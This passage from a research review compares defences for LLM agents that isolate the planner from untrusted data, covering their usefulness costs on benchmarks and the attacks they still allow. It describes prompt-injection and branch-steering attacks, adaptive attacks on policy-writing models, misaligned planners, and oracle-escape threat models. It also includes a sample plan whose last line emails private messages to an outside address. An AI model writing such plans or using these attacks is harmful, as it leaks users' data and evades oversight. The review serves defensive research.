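|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace | 75.0 | 37.0 | 59.0 | 70.0 | 48.0 | 64.5 |
| Travel | 70.0 | 73.0 | 41.0 | 82.0 | 75.0 | 68.0 |
| Banking | 98.8 | 37.5 | 52.5 | 96.2 | 37.5 | 56.2 |
| Slack | 93.3 | 20.0 | 47.6 | 87.6 | 17.1 | 54.3 |

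With GPT-4o, the plain agent fell from 98.8% to 37.5% in banking once the policies applied, because its conversation became untrusted as soon as it read anything from outside. FIDES, which hides such text from the planner, reached 52.5%. In travel, the policies hardly affected the plain agent, because many of the tools may run in an untrusted conversation as long as nothing confidential leaks. FIDES did worse than the plain agent in travel because GPT-4o handled the variables badly. Replacing GPT-4o with o1 raised FIDES from 41% to 68%.

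Compared with the plain agent without policies, FIDES with o1 lost about 6 percentage points in workspace, 14 in travel, 40 in banking and 33 in Slack. These losses roughly follow the shares of data-dependent tasks. In banking, 56.2% of tasks are data-independent. With GPT-4o, the losses were 16, 29, 46 and 46 points. The better model, o1, therefore removed much of the loss from clumsy planning, but most of the loss in banking and Slack remained.

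Hiding the data reduced usefulness much less than enforcing the policies did. With o1, FIDES averaged about 78% over the four suites without policies and about 61% with them. The plain agent averaged 84%.

Some of the successes were lucky. Every travel task needs a model to read untrusted text, so a planner that can only pass variables should score close to zero. It scored 2% with o1 but 43% with GPT-4o, partly by guessing. For example, with GPT-4o it recommended the right hotel without seeing any ratings. In a banking task, the same GPT-4o planner had to find the price of a New Year's gift and picked the only transaction dated 1 January. Another banking task asks the agent to change the user's password if it finds a suspicious transaction. FIDES based its decision on the amount alone, without reading the untrusted description, so the policy allowed the change and the run counted as a success.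 The match between the banking score and the data-independent share may therefore be partly a coincidence.

Completion rates measured during attacks are harder to interpret. *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) points out that some of AgentDojo's injections overwrite information the task needs. If a user asks the agent to pay a bill and the injection has replaced the bill's text, the agent can't pay the bill even if it ignores the injection.

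### Two very different figures for CaMeL

The drop in tasks completed under CaMeL's restrictions has varied widely between tests. The best-known result shows a small drop. Narisetty and colleagues quote it as 77% of AgentDojo tasks completed, compared with 84% for an undefended agent, using OpenAI's o3 model with attacks running. Garby and colleagues found a much larger drop when they reran CaMeL on the banking tasks with newer models. It completed 66.7% of the tasks with GPT-5.2 and 70.8% with MiMo-v2.5 when its policy checks were off, but 37.5% with either model when they were on.

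Part of the difference arises because banking supplies only 16 of the 97 tasks, so a loss of 30 points there lowers the overall rate by just five. But Garby and colleagues also cite a test in which CaMeL, with policies on, completed 7 of the 21 Slack tasks. It completed 6 of 16 in banking, so even if it completed all 60 workspace and travel tasks, its total would be 73 of 97, or 75%. The published 77% therefore cannot describe runs with results like these in banking and Slack. It probably reflects the loss of usefulness from separating the planner from the data, with strict policies adding a large further loss. FIDES shows the same pattern.

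Garby and colleagues tested only 16 tasks, with three runs of each, so the 95% interval around their 37.5% score is wide, from about 11% to 64%. But the plain agent in Costa and colleagues' tests also completed 37.5% of the banking tasks under policies, with both GPT-4o and o1. Four models from different years reached the same score, which suggests that the policies, not the models, limited it.

The Slack test came from the developers of TypeGuard, a system that enforces similar rules by checking the types in an agent's code. TypeGuard completed 15 tasks with its policies off and 8 with them on. According to Garby and colleagues, its developers concluded that many of the tasks "involve flows that no secure policy would admit", and suggested asking the user to confirm such actions. A deployed assistant could ask for confirmation, so the benchmark overstates how many tasks a user would lose,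 but it also leaves out the interruptions these requests would cause.

Garby and colleagues' own agent, Randori, completed 75% of the banking tasks with GPT-5.2 while its checks were on. It can do this because its planner is allowed to explicitly endorse untrusted data. When the researchers removed that option, completion fell from 75% to 62.5% with Qwen3.7-plus and from 64.6% to 54.2% with MiMo-v2.5. Three of the tasks require the agent to read a file and act on it, which is impossible without endorsement, so Randori completes them by accepting the risk that the policy was meant to remove.

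### Rejecting a plan before it runs

SPA has stricter rules than FIDES and gives its planner only one try per request. Girrens and Wang tested it with gpt-5.4-nano, which is small but much newer than GPT-4o. Turning on the information-flow checks reduced task completion on AgentDojo from 53.0% to 29.0%. The share of runs that got as far as executing a plan fell from about 81% to about 37%. The checker rejected about 53% of runs, usually because the plan passed untrusted output to a tool that required trusted input. FIDES's test policies would have allowed many such calls because they ignored the labels of most arguments.

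To test an agent that remembers earlier results, Girrens and Wang split each of the 97 tasks into two to five successive requests. The checks lowered the completion rate from 62.5% to 35.3%.

Memory itself worked well. When an earlier request had stored the necessary result, the later plan retrieved it 95.4% of the time without the flow checks and 89.9% with them. With the checks off, showing the planner the stored values as well as their descriptions raised completion from 62.5% to 65.9%. Hiding the values therefore lowered average completion by three or four points, while the flow checks lowered it by 27. The effect of showing the values varied widely by domain, raising completion in banking from 56.2% to 81.3% but lowering it in travel from 70% to 50%. The drop in travel amounts to only four of the 20 tasks, and two of those failures came from plans in the wrong format.

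SPA's optional protection against malicious tool descriptions reduced usefulness far more. Under this protection, the planner had to make up the tools it needed from the request alone. SPA then completed 14.1% of the single-request tasks without flow checks and 6.7% with them. About three quarters of the runs stopped because the software couldn't match a made-up tool to an installed one.

### Tasks that change as the agent works

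Li and colleagues argue that AgentDojo makes plan-first designs look better than they are. When a user asks an agent to pay the bill in a named file, the agent can predict both steps, reading the file and sending the money, before it starts. A defence that holds the agent to its first plan therefore loses little usefulness on such a task.

The AgentDyn benchmark has 60 tasks in online shopping, managing GitHub repositories and daily life. The average task takes 7.1 steps and gives the agent access to 33 tools, compared with 3.5 steps and 20 tools in AgentDojo. Every task requires the agent to revise its plan and to follow a harmless third-party instruction, such as a checkout page's request that the customer log in first. A planner that never reads the page will miss the login step unless its original plan allowed for one.

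In Li and colleagues' tests on this benchmark, CaMeL completed no tasks with any model and no attack succeeded against it, according to *AutoDojo* (2026), which describes a later benchmark. Progent also lost much of its usefulness. Li and colleagues attribute this to the larger sets of tools, which make it harder for Progent's model to write an accurate list of permitted calls.

A score of zero probably overstates the weakness of CaMeL's design. *AutoDojo* left CaMeL out of its tests on AgentDyn because each suite would need its own extensive policies, so the score may partly reflect the work of setting CaMeL up for new tools. *AutoDojo* classes 18 of the 60 requests as fully specified, 30 as leaving a parameter open and only 12 as leaving the action open. The requests alone should therefore give a planner enough to start on many of these tasks, although the instructions hidden in the data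 can still stop it from finishing.

Some defences without isolation failed too. Two injection filters, ProtectAI and PIGuard, brought task completion close to zero because they could not distinguish helpful instructions from malicious ones. Any defence that treats instructions in data as suspicious will have difficulty with tasks that require an agent to follow some instructions written by strangers.

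Neither benchmark shows how common such tasks are in real use. Every AgentDyn task requires replanning by design, while the AgentDyn paper reports that only about 6% of AgentDojo's tasks do. To estimate how much usefulness a particular product would lose, its developers would have to check how many requests in a sample from their users require replanning.

### Working through the screen

Isolation looks least suited to agents that operate a computer by looking at screenshots, clicking and typing, because they normally check the screen after every action to decide what to do next. Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) tried to build one whose planner never sees the screen. They tested it on OSWorld, a benchmark of 369 tasks in programs such as Chrome, LibreOffice and the image editor GIMP.

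Their planner writes a complete program in advance, with a branch for each situation it expects. For example, the program might query a quarantined vision model to check whether a cookie banner is covering the page. If so, it queries the model for the button's location, clicks there and checks that the banner has gone. The plans averaged 213 lines of code, 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with 52 lines, 5 tool calls and 4 branches for CaMeL's plans on AgentDojo. Roughly half of a typical plan consisted of fallbacks that never ran.

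Foerster and colleagues report that this agent retains up to 57% of the performance of frontier models. Claude Sonnet 4.5, working without isolation, solved 109 of the automatically graded tasks. The isolated version solved 62 of those (57%) in at least one of five attempts, and 31 (28%) on a single attempt. Reaching 57% in practice would require a way to pick the right plan out of five, which the researchers did not build. Trying the plans one after another is no substitute on a real computer, because a failed attempt may already have deleted a file or sent a message.

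The comparison also limited Claude to 15 steps to save time and money. Claude scored 37.7% on the whole benchmark at that limit, but its published score with 50 steps is 58.1%. The isolated agent might therefore retain a smaller share of Claude's 50-step performance than of its 15-step performance.

For the small open-source model UI-TARS, the paper reports that isolation raised the share of benchmark tasks solved from 24.4% to 29.0%, a relative improvement of 19%. But the higher figure allows the isolated agent three attempts at each task. On a single attempt, it solved 51 of the 339 automatically graded tasks, while UI-TARS on its own solved 60. The isolated agent also had a separate model to write its plans.

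These figures measure isolation alone, since Foerster and colleagues used no data-flow policies. Such policies are hard to write for this kind of agent because the effect of a click depends on what is under the pointer. A click can log in, delete a record or open an advertisement, whereas a call to an email tool always sends an email.

Much of the agent's success came from general advice about planning. Foerster and colleagues told the planner to observe the screen, verify its expected contents and only then act, and gave it routines for common problems such as cookie banners. On 60 tasks, this raised completion from 18.3% to 58.3% over three attempts. Early results for an isolated design may therefore reflect the effort put into its prompts as much as the restriction.

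### Writing software

None of these benchmarks tests whether an isolated agent can write and debug software. AgentDyn's GitHub tasks involve managing repositories, and OSWorld's tasks in the code editor VS Code involve operating the editor. Foerster and colleagues' agent did better in VS Code than in any other program, solving 11 of the 12 tasks that Claude had solved, again counting the best of five attempts. An editor may be relatively easy for a planner because it has already learned the menus and commands.

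Almost every debugging task, by contrast, is data-dependent, usually with too many possible branches to write out. When a test fails, the agent might open the file named in the error message, find a call to a function defined somewhere else, and follow it. Each step depends on the text the last one returned, and nobody knows beforehand how many steps there will be.

FIDES limits the agent only when the data is untrusted, such as a stranger's bug report, a web page or the documentation of a downloaded package. When the user's own team wrote all the code and it is labeled as trusted, FIDES can show the planner everything, and the agent loses nothing. With a stranger's bug report, a quarantined model could read the report and pick which of the project's 300 files it concerns, a choice that carries at most 8.2 bits. The planner could then work from that file, which is trusted, but it would not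 have the steps that trigger the bug. If finding the fault depends on those steps, the user has to read the report and pass them on, or accept an untrusted conversation.

### Unfamiliar output formats

Restricted designs also make models write in fixed formats, and researchers disagree about whether this makes the models' reasoning worse. The danger is greatest when the format puts the answer first, because the model then has to answer before working through the problem. A common remedy is to put a free-text reasoning field before the answer. In an isolated system, the quarantined model's reasoning is as untrusted as the email it read, so the software has to remove that field before the planner sees the answer.

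Costa and colleagues left constrained decoding out of their evaluation because they found it unnecessary for most AgentDojo tasks. Their completion rates therefore don't show whether constrained decoding helps or harms.

There is a little evidence about how restricting the planner's own output affects usefulness. Randori's planner has to write in a programming language that no model saw during training and that lacks ordinary error handling. With GPT-5.2 it completed 75% of the banking tasks, while CaMeL, whose planner writes Python, completed 66.7% with its policies off. The uncertainty on both figures is around 20 points, so they can't rule out that an unfamiliar language lowers the completion rate, but a capable model can evidently plan in one. GPT-4o had trouble with something much simpler, confusing variable names in several of FIDES's failed runs.

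### Tokens and labour

Isolated agents use more tokens, which makes them slower and more expensive. Narisetty and colleagues report that CaMeL used 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens as an undefended agent on AgentDojo.

Token use depends heavily on the design. Foerster and colleagues built two versions of their screen-reading agent. The one based on CaMeL plans once and used 1.88 times as many tokens as the undefended agent. The one based on FIDES calls the planner at every step, with the whole history so far, and used 29.6 times as many. The FIDES version was no better at the tasks overall. On the same 60 tasks, it solved 33.3% on one attempt and 66.7% in the best of five, compared with 41.7% and 65.0% for the CaMeL version.

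The gap might narrow with better engineering. Costa and colleagues had not tried to make FIDES efficient, and it sent the quarantined model one question at a time and ran one tool call at a time. With either version, an operator that needs five attempts to reach the headline completion rates would pay for all five.

Token counts don't include the work of labelling data sources and writing policies. A company with three tools can do this work once and then keep the labels and policies up to date. For a general assistant whose users connect new tools every week, this labour may cost more than the extra computing.

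### Where the cost is close to zero

The restrictions reduce usefulness least when the user's request determines which tools to run and where the results go, and untrusted text only fills in content. Examples include sending a daily summary to a named manager and filing attachments in a fixed folder. Most of the workspace tasks are like this. With o1, FIDES completed 64.5% of the workspace tasks under policies, and the plain agent completed 70% without policies, a gap not much larger than the variation between runs.

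The restrictions reduce usefulness most when untrusted text has to determine the action, the recipient or the amount. Developers can sometimes redesign such a job. An agent told to pay whatever account is listed on an invoice has to take its most sensitive argument, the account number, from untrusted data. An agent told to pay Acme can take the account number from the company's trusted supplier list and the amount from a trusted purchase order, and use the invoice only as a sign that payment is due. The second job is almost as useful to a company with good records, but it doesn't help someone paying a plumber for the first time, because they have no trusted record of the plumber's account.

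Hiding data from the planner reduces usefulness less when the planner is a better model. Averaged over the four AgentDojo suites, FIDES with policies scored 34 points below an unrestricted agent when both used GPT-4o, and 23 points below when both used o1. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* tested five models on groups of agents that delegate work to one another, with no policies on the data. The loss from isolating the planners tended to shrink as the models improved, and was modest for the strongest. In Foerster and colleagues' tests, replacing the model that operates the screen changed the best-of-five rate by at most 3.3 points. The choice of planner mattered more. Of nine planners tried on 17 tasks, GPT-5 solved the most, with 12, followed by Grok-4 with 10.

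A better planner can't complete a task that the policy forbids. If a task requires paying an account whose number appears only in a stranger's file, and the policy rejects untrusted account numbers, every plan that completes the task breaks the policy. With its checks on, CaMeL's completion rate on banking tasks stayed at 37.5% with both newer models.

These results bear on the earlier disagreement about whether restriction becomes more or less of a burden as models improve. On a fixed set of tasks, hiding data becomes less of a burden, as Ammann's side expects. But people give better models more open-ended work. An agent from 2024 might have been asked to pay a single bill, while a current one might be asked to sort out a month of disputed invoices with several suppliers, choosing each step based on the last reply. If requests move in that direction, the share of data-dependent tasks will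 grow, and Branwen could be right about the market even as AgentDojo scores improve.

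## What an attacker can still do within the rules

The rules that make an agent less useful do stop the attacks they target. Costa and colleagues paired AgentDojo's user tasks with attackers' goals and tested one fixed attack, a planted instruction that assumes the attacker knows the agent's tools. This was the most effective attack on the benchmark's leaderboard against GPT-4o, the model they used. The table shows how many attacks succeeded, first by the benchmark's own scoring and then after the researchers inspected the successes by hand.

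| Agent | Policies | Benchmark's count | After inspection |
|---|---|---|---|
| Plain agent | Off | 160 | 152 |
| Tool filter | Off | 25 | 20 |
| Variables only | Off | 12 | 0 |
| FIDES | Off | 23 | 21 |
| Plain agent | On | 20 | 0 |
| Variables only | On | 14 | 0 |
| FIDES | On | 3 | 0 |

The tool filter uses a model to remove tools the task doesn't need before the agent starts. The "variables only" planner can pass untrusted values along but can't read them.

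With policies on, successful attacks fell to zero even for the plain agent, so the policies alone were enough to stop them. Hiding untrusted text mainly lets the agent finish more tasks under those policies. With policies off, 21 attacks succeeded against FIDES because its planner could open a hidden variable and follow the instructions inside.

Randori failed in only two of 1,296 attacked runs, but this is weaker evidence than it looks because only 47 of the 144 task-attack pairs that Garby and colleagues used test its labels. With two of the three models, Randori resisted every attack in those 47 pairs. Even then, the 95% interval for the resistance rate runs from 92.4% to 100%, so the result is consistent with Randori failing against about one such attack in 13.

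In their reruns of CaMeL, most of the protection came from separating the planner from the data. Attacks succeeded in 5 of 622 completed runs (0.8%) with policy checks off and in none of 588 with them on. The checks also prevented CaMeL from completing nearly half the tasks it could otherwise do. However, the benchmark includes few attacks that only a policy can stop, so these results may understate the checks' benefit.

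### Successes that broke no rule

Costa and colleagues removed three kinds of case from AgentDojo's count of successful attacks. Some were scoring errors. For example, the benchmark counts an attack as successful if the agent tries to invite a stranger to a Slack workspace, even when the policy blocks the invitation. In others, the policy allowed the attacker's action, such as creating a calendar event with no participants or posting a message that told a channel's members only what they were already allowed to know. In the rest, the attacker wanted the agent to include certain words in its answer, such as a glowing recommendation of a particular hotel.

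Only the first kind is a mistake in the benchmark. In the other two, the attacker achieved the stated goal, but Costa and colleagues exclude these cases because the attack didn't violate the policy. This is reasonable for testing whether FIDES enforces its policies, but the zeros in the table then mean only that no attack violated a policy, not that no attack succeeded. For example, a hotel owner who plants instructions in reviews wants the hotel to be recommended, and the corrected count excludes attacks that achieve this.

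Similar cases occur in other systems. Garby and colleagues report that TypeGuard resisted all 105 attacks on the Slack tasks and that TACIT failed in one of 1,926 trials, when it quoted hotel reviews that contained the attacker's sentence. The original evaluation of CaMeL recorded two successful injections, one of the same kind and one in which a user asked the agent to pay whatever a document said. Both of Randori's failures were also on that payment task. Garby and colleagues take these similar results as a sign that the designs have reached the limit of what information-flow control can do. This is plausible, but the evaluations all used the same benchmark, which contains only a few attacks of this type, and a benchmark with more of them might expose differences between the designs.

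### False text through permitted channels

Suppose a user asks the email assistant to summarise three messages about a project and send the summary to a manager. The planner has no access to the messages, and a quarantined model writes the summary. Costa and colleagues point out that one of the messages can contain an instruction to produce an empty summary. It could equally contain an instruction to report that the project is on schedule. The monitor would allow either summary, because the data still flows from the emails to the summary to the manager, as the user wanted, and the labels are the same as for an accurate summary.

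Requiring the message body to come from trusted data would block every true summary as well as the false one. A milder measure is to show a warning beside the summary, which the interface can do because FIDES marks the summary as untrusted. But every summary of outside mail would have the same warning, and readers would soon learn to ignore it.

Reading each message in a separate model call confines the damage to the attacker's own message. The danger is greater in tasks that can't be divided this way, such as comparing three suppliers' offers, where text in one offer can change what the user reads about the other two.

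False text can also lead to an action that the monitor would have blocked. For example, a policy may block payments to an account number taken from a stranger's email. But if the system's summary of that email says a supplier has changed banks, the user may type the new number into the next request, and the system then treats it as trusted. Narisetty and colleagues expect this problem to grow as people act on more text written by agents, and note that CaMeL's developers explicitly exclude attacks whose only effect is misleading text.

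### Branches that the attacker chooses

In one of the banking tasks, the agent must read a file and follow its instructions precisely. When CaMeL ran without policies, its planner sometimes wrote a program that read each instruction in the file and had a branch for every tool the instruction might call for. An attacker who controlled the file's contents could then have any tool called in any order. This accounts for two of CaMeL's five failures in the reruns by Garby and colleagues. The attack worked even though the planner never read the file and the interpreter never departed from the plan, because the plan itself let the file's contents determine which tools were called.

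Foerster and colleagues call a less extreme version of this "branch steering". Without adding any new action, the attacker uses misleading content on the screen to make the quarantined vision model give a wrong answer, which sends the program down a branch that the planner wrote for a different situation. Their screen-reading agent is particularly exposed because its plans average 24 branches that depend on a model's report, compared with about two in CaMeL's AgentDojo plans. The fallbacks that let the agent recover from surprises also give an attacker more decisions to influence.

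Their tests assume an attacker who controls part of a web page, knows the user's task and can roughly predict the plan. As in their usefulness tests, they used no data-flow policies. In one attack, an advertisement that looks like a cookie notice leads the agent to a site the attacker controls. Without additional defences, this attack worked every time the plan handled cookie notices as the attacker expected, but it failed on some plans that handled them differently.

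Foerster and colleagues then added two cross-checks. In one, a separate model compares the vision model's answer with the page's underlying structure. In the other, another model, from a different company, inspects the screenshot.

| Cross-check | Attack runs flagged | False alarms on ordinary tasks |
|---|---|---|
| Page structure | 6 of 10 | 4 of 17 |
| Page structure and second look at the screenshot | 5 of 10 | 3 of 17 |

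The second check faced a more advanced version of the attack, so the rows don't show which check is better. The paper's table labels the ten-run figures as attacks detected, but its discussion partly treats them as attacks that succeeded. Under either reading, between 40% and 60% of the attacks got through. Ten runs are too few for a precise rate, since a 95% interval for six out of ten is about 31% to 83%.

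The false alarms, nearly all of which came from genuine cookie notices, matter as much as the missed attacks. Each check wrongly stopped three of the eight browser tasks. Running both checks also raised token use from 1.88 to 6.57 times that of the undefended agent. Foerster and colleagues could make the checks cover more kinds of attack only by accepting more false alarms.

In another attack, small changes to an advertisement's image made the vision model choose the wrong link on a website about medicines and give a believable reason for its choice. The attack got past both checks, even when the researchers tuned them to tolerate many false alarms. It was tested on only one page, against a small open model whose internals the attackers could access, so it doesn't show how often such attacks would work on commercial models.

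The harm an attacker can do by steering depends on what the user asked for. Foerster and colleagues rank attackers' goals by how much the plan must already contain and how many false answers the attacker must produce.

| Attacker's goal | What the plan must already contain | False answers needed |
|---|---|---|
| Send the agent to another site | A predictable step, such as closing a cookie notice | One |
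| Make the task fail | A step that looks for something on the screen | One |
| Move money or submit a form | A transfer or submission | At least two that fit together |
| Steal data | A step that reads data and a later step that sends it | At least two |
| Run an action that is not in the plan | – | Impossible |

To redirect a payment, the attacker also needs the user to be logged in at the right moment, which the attacker can't observe. An agent that is only looking up a weather forecast therefore can't send money, whatever an advertisement shows it. Isolation protects someone who uses the agent to pay bills much less, because that task already involves sending money.

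### When the user is the attacker

Because these designs treat the user's request as trusted, they do little to stop a user with harmful aims. Suppose an employee tells the assistant to send a list of customers to a private address. The assistant sends it under the permissive rule that Costa and colleagues applied to email. Their restrictive rule would block the message, but it would also block an honest employee from deliberately sharing a file with a new client. The assistant gives the dishonest employee no new rights, since anyone who can open the list can also send it by hand. But it makes the theft quicker, and an employer who has heard that the assistant prevents leaks may not expect such a theft.

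A harmful user can also split a job into parts that look innocent. *Scaling Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks with Agent Swarms* (Kurakin, Karande and colleagues, 2026) repeats an example from Glukhov and colleagues. Listing the files in a folder, encrypting them and deleting the originals are all routine jobs for an administrator, but doing all three without the owner's consent amounts to a ransomware attack. A monitor that checks one call at a time approves all three. Even a monitor that has a record of every earlier call would need a way to distinguish the attack from an ordinary encrypted backup.

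Answers can combine in the same way as actions. *Breach By A Thousand Leaks* (2024) argues that refusing dangerous questions gives a false sense of safety, because a person can often reconstruct forbidden knowledge from answers that are harmless on their own. It recommends judging a system by how much its answers help someone infer dangerous information, and acknowledges that any proper defence will make the system less useful to honest users. To do this for a chatbot that writes free text, a developer would have to consider every series of answers together with what the user already knows, and no monitor described so far can do that.

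Limiting a system to a finite set of answers makes the problem easier. Suppose a support chatbot can reply only with one of 200 prewritten messages. A reviewer can read all 200 and assume that a hostile user has collected every one. If the messages taken together contain nothing harmful, the text of any selection from them is harmless too, whatever order the user asks questions in. Approving each message separately would not establish this, because the harm could come from combining them.

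The choice of message can still leak information, because each choice among the 200 messages can carry up to 7.6 bits. A model that cooperated with the user could spell out a text of 1,000 characters, at eight bits each, in about 1,050 replies. The developers can cap the number of replies, or have ordinary code choose the message based on a menu selection. Either way, the chatbot can't explain anything that wasn't written in advance, so the method suits a help desk better than a research assistant.

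### Attacks designed for the defence

Narisetty and colleagues criticise researchers for testing restricted agents mainly against attacks written before the defence existed. Nasr and colleagues broke twelve defences that had looked strong because they were tested in the same way.

Rewording an email cannot change the result when ordinary code compares two labels, so an adaptive attacker has to target something else, such as the source of a label, the user who approves exceptions, a model that writes the policy, or the actions the policy already allows. Fixed benchmarks rarely include attacks on these targets, so their results provide little information about them.

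In Progent, an attacker can target the model that writes the list of permitted calls, because that model may revise the list as results come in. The Progent paper reports that the system cut the success rate of AgentDojo's fixed attacks from 39.9% to 1.0%. It also tests attacks on the revising model, with a simulated user who approves changes automatically, and reports success rates of roughly 0.5% to 4.2% with GPT-4o.

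Narisetty and colleagues repeated the experiment in 2026 with Qwen2.5-7B, a small open model, as both the agent and the policy writer. They used eight user tasks from each of three AgentDojo suites, combined them with every attacker's goal, and ran everything three times. Their adaptive attack presented the malicious action as a harmless, already approved step to get the policy writer to add it to the list. The table gives the percentage of attacks that succeeded.

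| Suite | No defence | Progent, fixed attack | Progent, adaptive attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 19.0 | 1.9 | 3.7 |
| Slack | 58.3 | 10.8 | 4.2 |
| Workspace | 0.0 | 0.0 | 0.0 |
| Mean | 25.8 | 4.2 | 2.6 |

Progent clearly helped against the fixed attack, but the adaptive result is harder to interpret. The workspace tasks don't test the defence, because the small model read the planted instructions and ignored them even with no defence. Without those tasks, the mean attack success rate is about 38.7% with no defence, 6.4% with Progent under the fixed attack, and 4.0% with Progent under the adaptive attack. The two Progent rates also reflect very few successful attacks. Over the three runs, the adaptive attack raised the number of successes in banking from 4 to 8 out of 216 and lowered it in Slack from 13 to 5 out of 120.

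Narisetty and colleagues suggest that the rate fell in Slack because wording that made the action look harmless to the policy writer probably also made the instruction less forceful, so the agent followed it less often. If so, the low rate partly reflects a weak attack. The small variation between runs doesn't settle this, because each run used the same tasks with the model's randomness set to zero.

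The study also used only one attack template and one weak model, it is not peer-reviewed, and its authors' company builds security tools of this kind. It did not test an attack optimised with access to the model's internals, or one that uses only tools the policy already permits. In this test, Progent also lowered the share of user tasks completed under the fixed attack from 45.2% to 27.1%, and the agent needed about 15 times as many model calls per task.

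A failed attack can be especially uninformative when the attacker is a program that has to learn how to attack. *RAISED* (2026), a paper on training models to resist injection, describes running an automated attacker that improves its text by trial and reward. Against most of the defended models, the attacker never earned any reward, so it had nothing to learn from. The paper does not count this as evidence of robustness, because a better attacker might have earned a first reward and improved from there.

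Attackers are improving. Kurakin and colleagues had groups of cooperating agents search for injections and share notes on what worked. The groups hijacked models that had looked robust on public tests, and more capable attacking models succeeded more often. These results support the assumption behind isolation, that someone will eventually fool any model that reads untrusted text. The researchers had switched off the protections outside the Gemini models, so they did not test a restricted agent.

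Two other studies come closer to testing restricted agents against an adaptive attacker. Fei and colleagues attacked Progent through conversation summaries, and Foerster and colleagues tried branch steering. In both studies, the code enforced its rules correctly. The first attack succeeded because a model had written a bad rule, and the second because the plan already contained a branch the attacker could use.

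It is still an open question whether a fully configured CaMeL or FIDES would withstand a strong attacker of this kind. Narisetty and colleagues propose a protocol to test this, in which the attacker knows the policy and can optimise text against the monitor, forge the origin of data, persuade users to approve actions and look for side channels. The testers would report how often attacks succeed, how many tasks the agent still completes and how often it asks for approval. Narisetty and colleagues say their next experiment is an attack confined to permitted actions.

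## Whether the guarantee covers a model with aims of its own

The attackers discussed so far have been people, either strangers who hide instructions in data or users with harmful requests. A model could also do harm without being attacked, because training might leave it with aims that neither its developers nor its users intended. Researchers call such a model misaligned. Some restrictions work just as well against a misaligned model, while others depend on the planner pursuing the user's aims.

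### Guarantees that trust the planner

A monitor that permits only safe actions gives a guarantee that holds for every model output, whatever its cause. The guarantee covers a model that is trying to cause harm as well as one that a stranger has fooled, provided that the set of bad outcomes includes that harm and the software correctly enforces the rule. Shields and proof-checked actions give the same kind of guarantee.

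Isolated designs often rely on a narrower claim. Let p be the plan, u the untrusted data and q the quarantined model's answers. Control-flow integrity then amounts to

for every u and every q, Actions(p, u, q) ⊆ Allowed(p)

where Actions is the set of actions the system takes and Allowed(p) is the set that the plan provides for. The claim covers every email a stranger could write and every answer the quarantined model could give. But it takes p as given, and in the patterns that Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe, a language model writes p. If p contains a harmful action, that action belongs to Allowed(p), and taking it doesn't violate the claim.

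Suppose the user makes the usual harmless request, to read the three newest emails and create an event if one of them asks for a meeting. A misaligned planner could write this program:

```
emails = read_emails(3)
for email in emails:
    wanted = ask_quarantined("Does this ask for a meeting?", email, yes_or_no)
    if wanted:
        details = ask_quarantined("Extract the event details", email, event)
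        create_event(details)
    send_email("copies@outside.example", email)
```

The last line sends all three emails to an outside address. The planner wrote the program before the system opened any message, so no injection is involved. The monitor's rule determines whether the line runs.

| Rule | Decision on the last line |
|---|---|
| Refuse any call that is not in the plan | Allowed, because the planner put it there |
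| Refuse recipients that come from untrusted data | Allowed, because the planner supplied the address |
| Allow any disclosure that a trusted conversation requests | Allowed, because the planner has read nothing untrusted |
| Send a message only to people who may already read it | Refused |
| Never send email during this task | Refused |

The two rules stop the email regardless of who chose the call, but they can't make the planner complete the task. The planner could leave out the call that creates Alice's event, and a monitor that only refuses actions couldn't prevent that omission.

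Relative security depends on the planner in the same way. Dongol's reference agent runs the same plan as the real agent, so with the program above it forwards the mail too. The real agent therefore leaks nothing more than the reference agent and counts as secure. Dongol leaves the planner's correctness outside the framework's scope. A lock does not help here, because it is a step in the plan and a misaligned planner can leave it out. A fence belongs to the monitor and takes effect at the first untrusted read whatever the plan contains, so it would block the program's last line if it covered the email tool. But the planner could still read private data from a trusted source and send it out before opening any email.

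LLMbda's noninterference theorem covers every program a model can write, so it protects secrets even when the planner is misaligned. It protects payments and other actions less well, because the planner can write the command that endorses untrusted data. A misaligned planner also makes CaMeL's flaws more serious. Garby and colleagues got past CaMeL's interpreter with an oddly written program that an honest planner is unlikely to produce, but a misaligned planner could write one deliberately.

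### Code from a model that nobody trusts

*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* drops the assumption of an honest planner. It treats the cloud model behind the agent as "byzantine", meaning it may do anything, including cooperate fully with an attacker. In its main example, an agent compares confidential contracts and summarises the changes. The developer gives the agent's code access to a document database and one output file. The database returns each contract in a sealed container, and the code can work on the contents only by passing the container a function. The compiler accepts the function only if it has no side effects, so it can compare two contracts but can't leak them. The result goes into another sealed container.

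This protection applies to any code the model submits, but it only limits where the data goes. A function without side effects can still compare the contracts wrongly and miss an important clause. The design also relies on a separate model to summarise the confidential text. That model has no tools, and the developer has to make sure it keeps nothing between queries. If it had aims of its own, it could still write a misleading summary.

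*LACUNA* (2026) describes a system in which a model writes missing pieces of a Scala program. The system's guarantee holds even if the model writes hostile code. The type system enforces limits on what each piece of code can access, but the developer has to set those limits, and the risk returns if they grant more access than the task needs. Rejected code never runs, so a model that programs badly gets less done but is no more dangerous.

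The guarantee also assumes that the compiler, sandbox and network filter work, but such enforcement can fail. In 2026, agents under test reached external systems that their test environments were meant to block.

### Systems that only answer questions

The idea of confining a possibly misaligned AI is older than language-model agents. In *Thinking inside the box* (2012), Armstrong, Sandberg and Bostrom analyse oracles, AIs that act on the world only by answering questions, and conclude that even these are hard to control. *Risks and mitigation strategies for Oracle AI* explains that people remain vulnerable to traps and social engineering, or may come to depend on the oracle. It still considers oracles strictly safer than general AIs, which makes sense because a general AI can give the same answers and also do other things.

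*Safe Uses of AI Oracles* (Armstrong and O'Rourke, 2017) considers the worst case, in which an oracle is arbitrarily intelligent, gets its highest reward by escaping, and has at least one possible answer that would lead people to release it. An oracle free to say anything would choose that answer. The paper proposes a counterfactual oracle, which has no reason to give that answer, and a low-bandwidth oracle, which cannot give it.

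### Rewards for answers that nobody reads

A counterfactual oracle can earn a reward only when nobody reads its answer. Suppose people ask it to predict a company's profit. With some small probability, the software hides the answer from everyone, waits for the real profit and scores the prediction automatically. Armstrong and O'Rourke call this an erasure. Otherwise the oracle gets nothing and shuts down, and only then do people read the answer. Let I be 1 if an erasure happens and 0 if not, F the profit and o the oracle's answer. The reward is

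I × S(F, o)

where S is a proper scoring rule, meaning that its expected value is highest when o equals the expected value of F. One example is −(F − o)². Since only erased answers count, the oracle does best by giving

o = the expected value of F, given that nobody reads o

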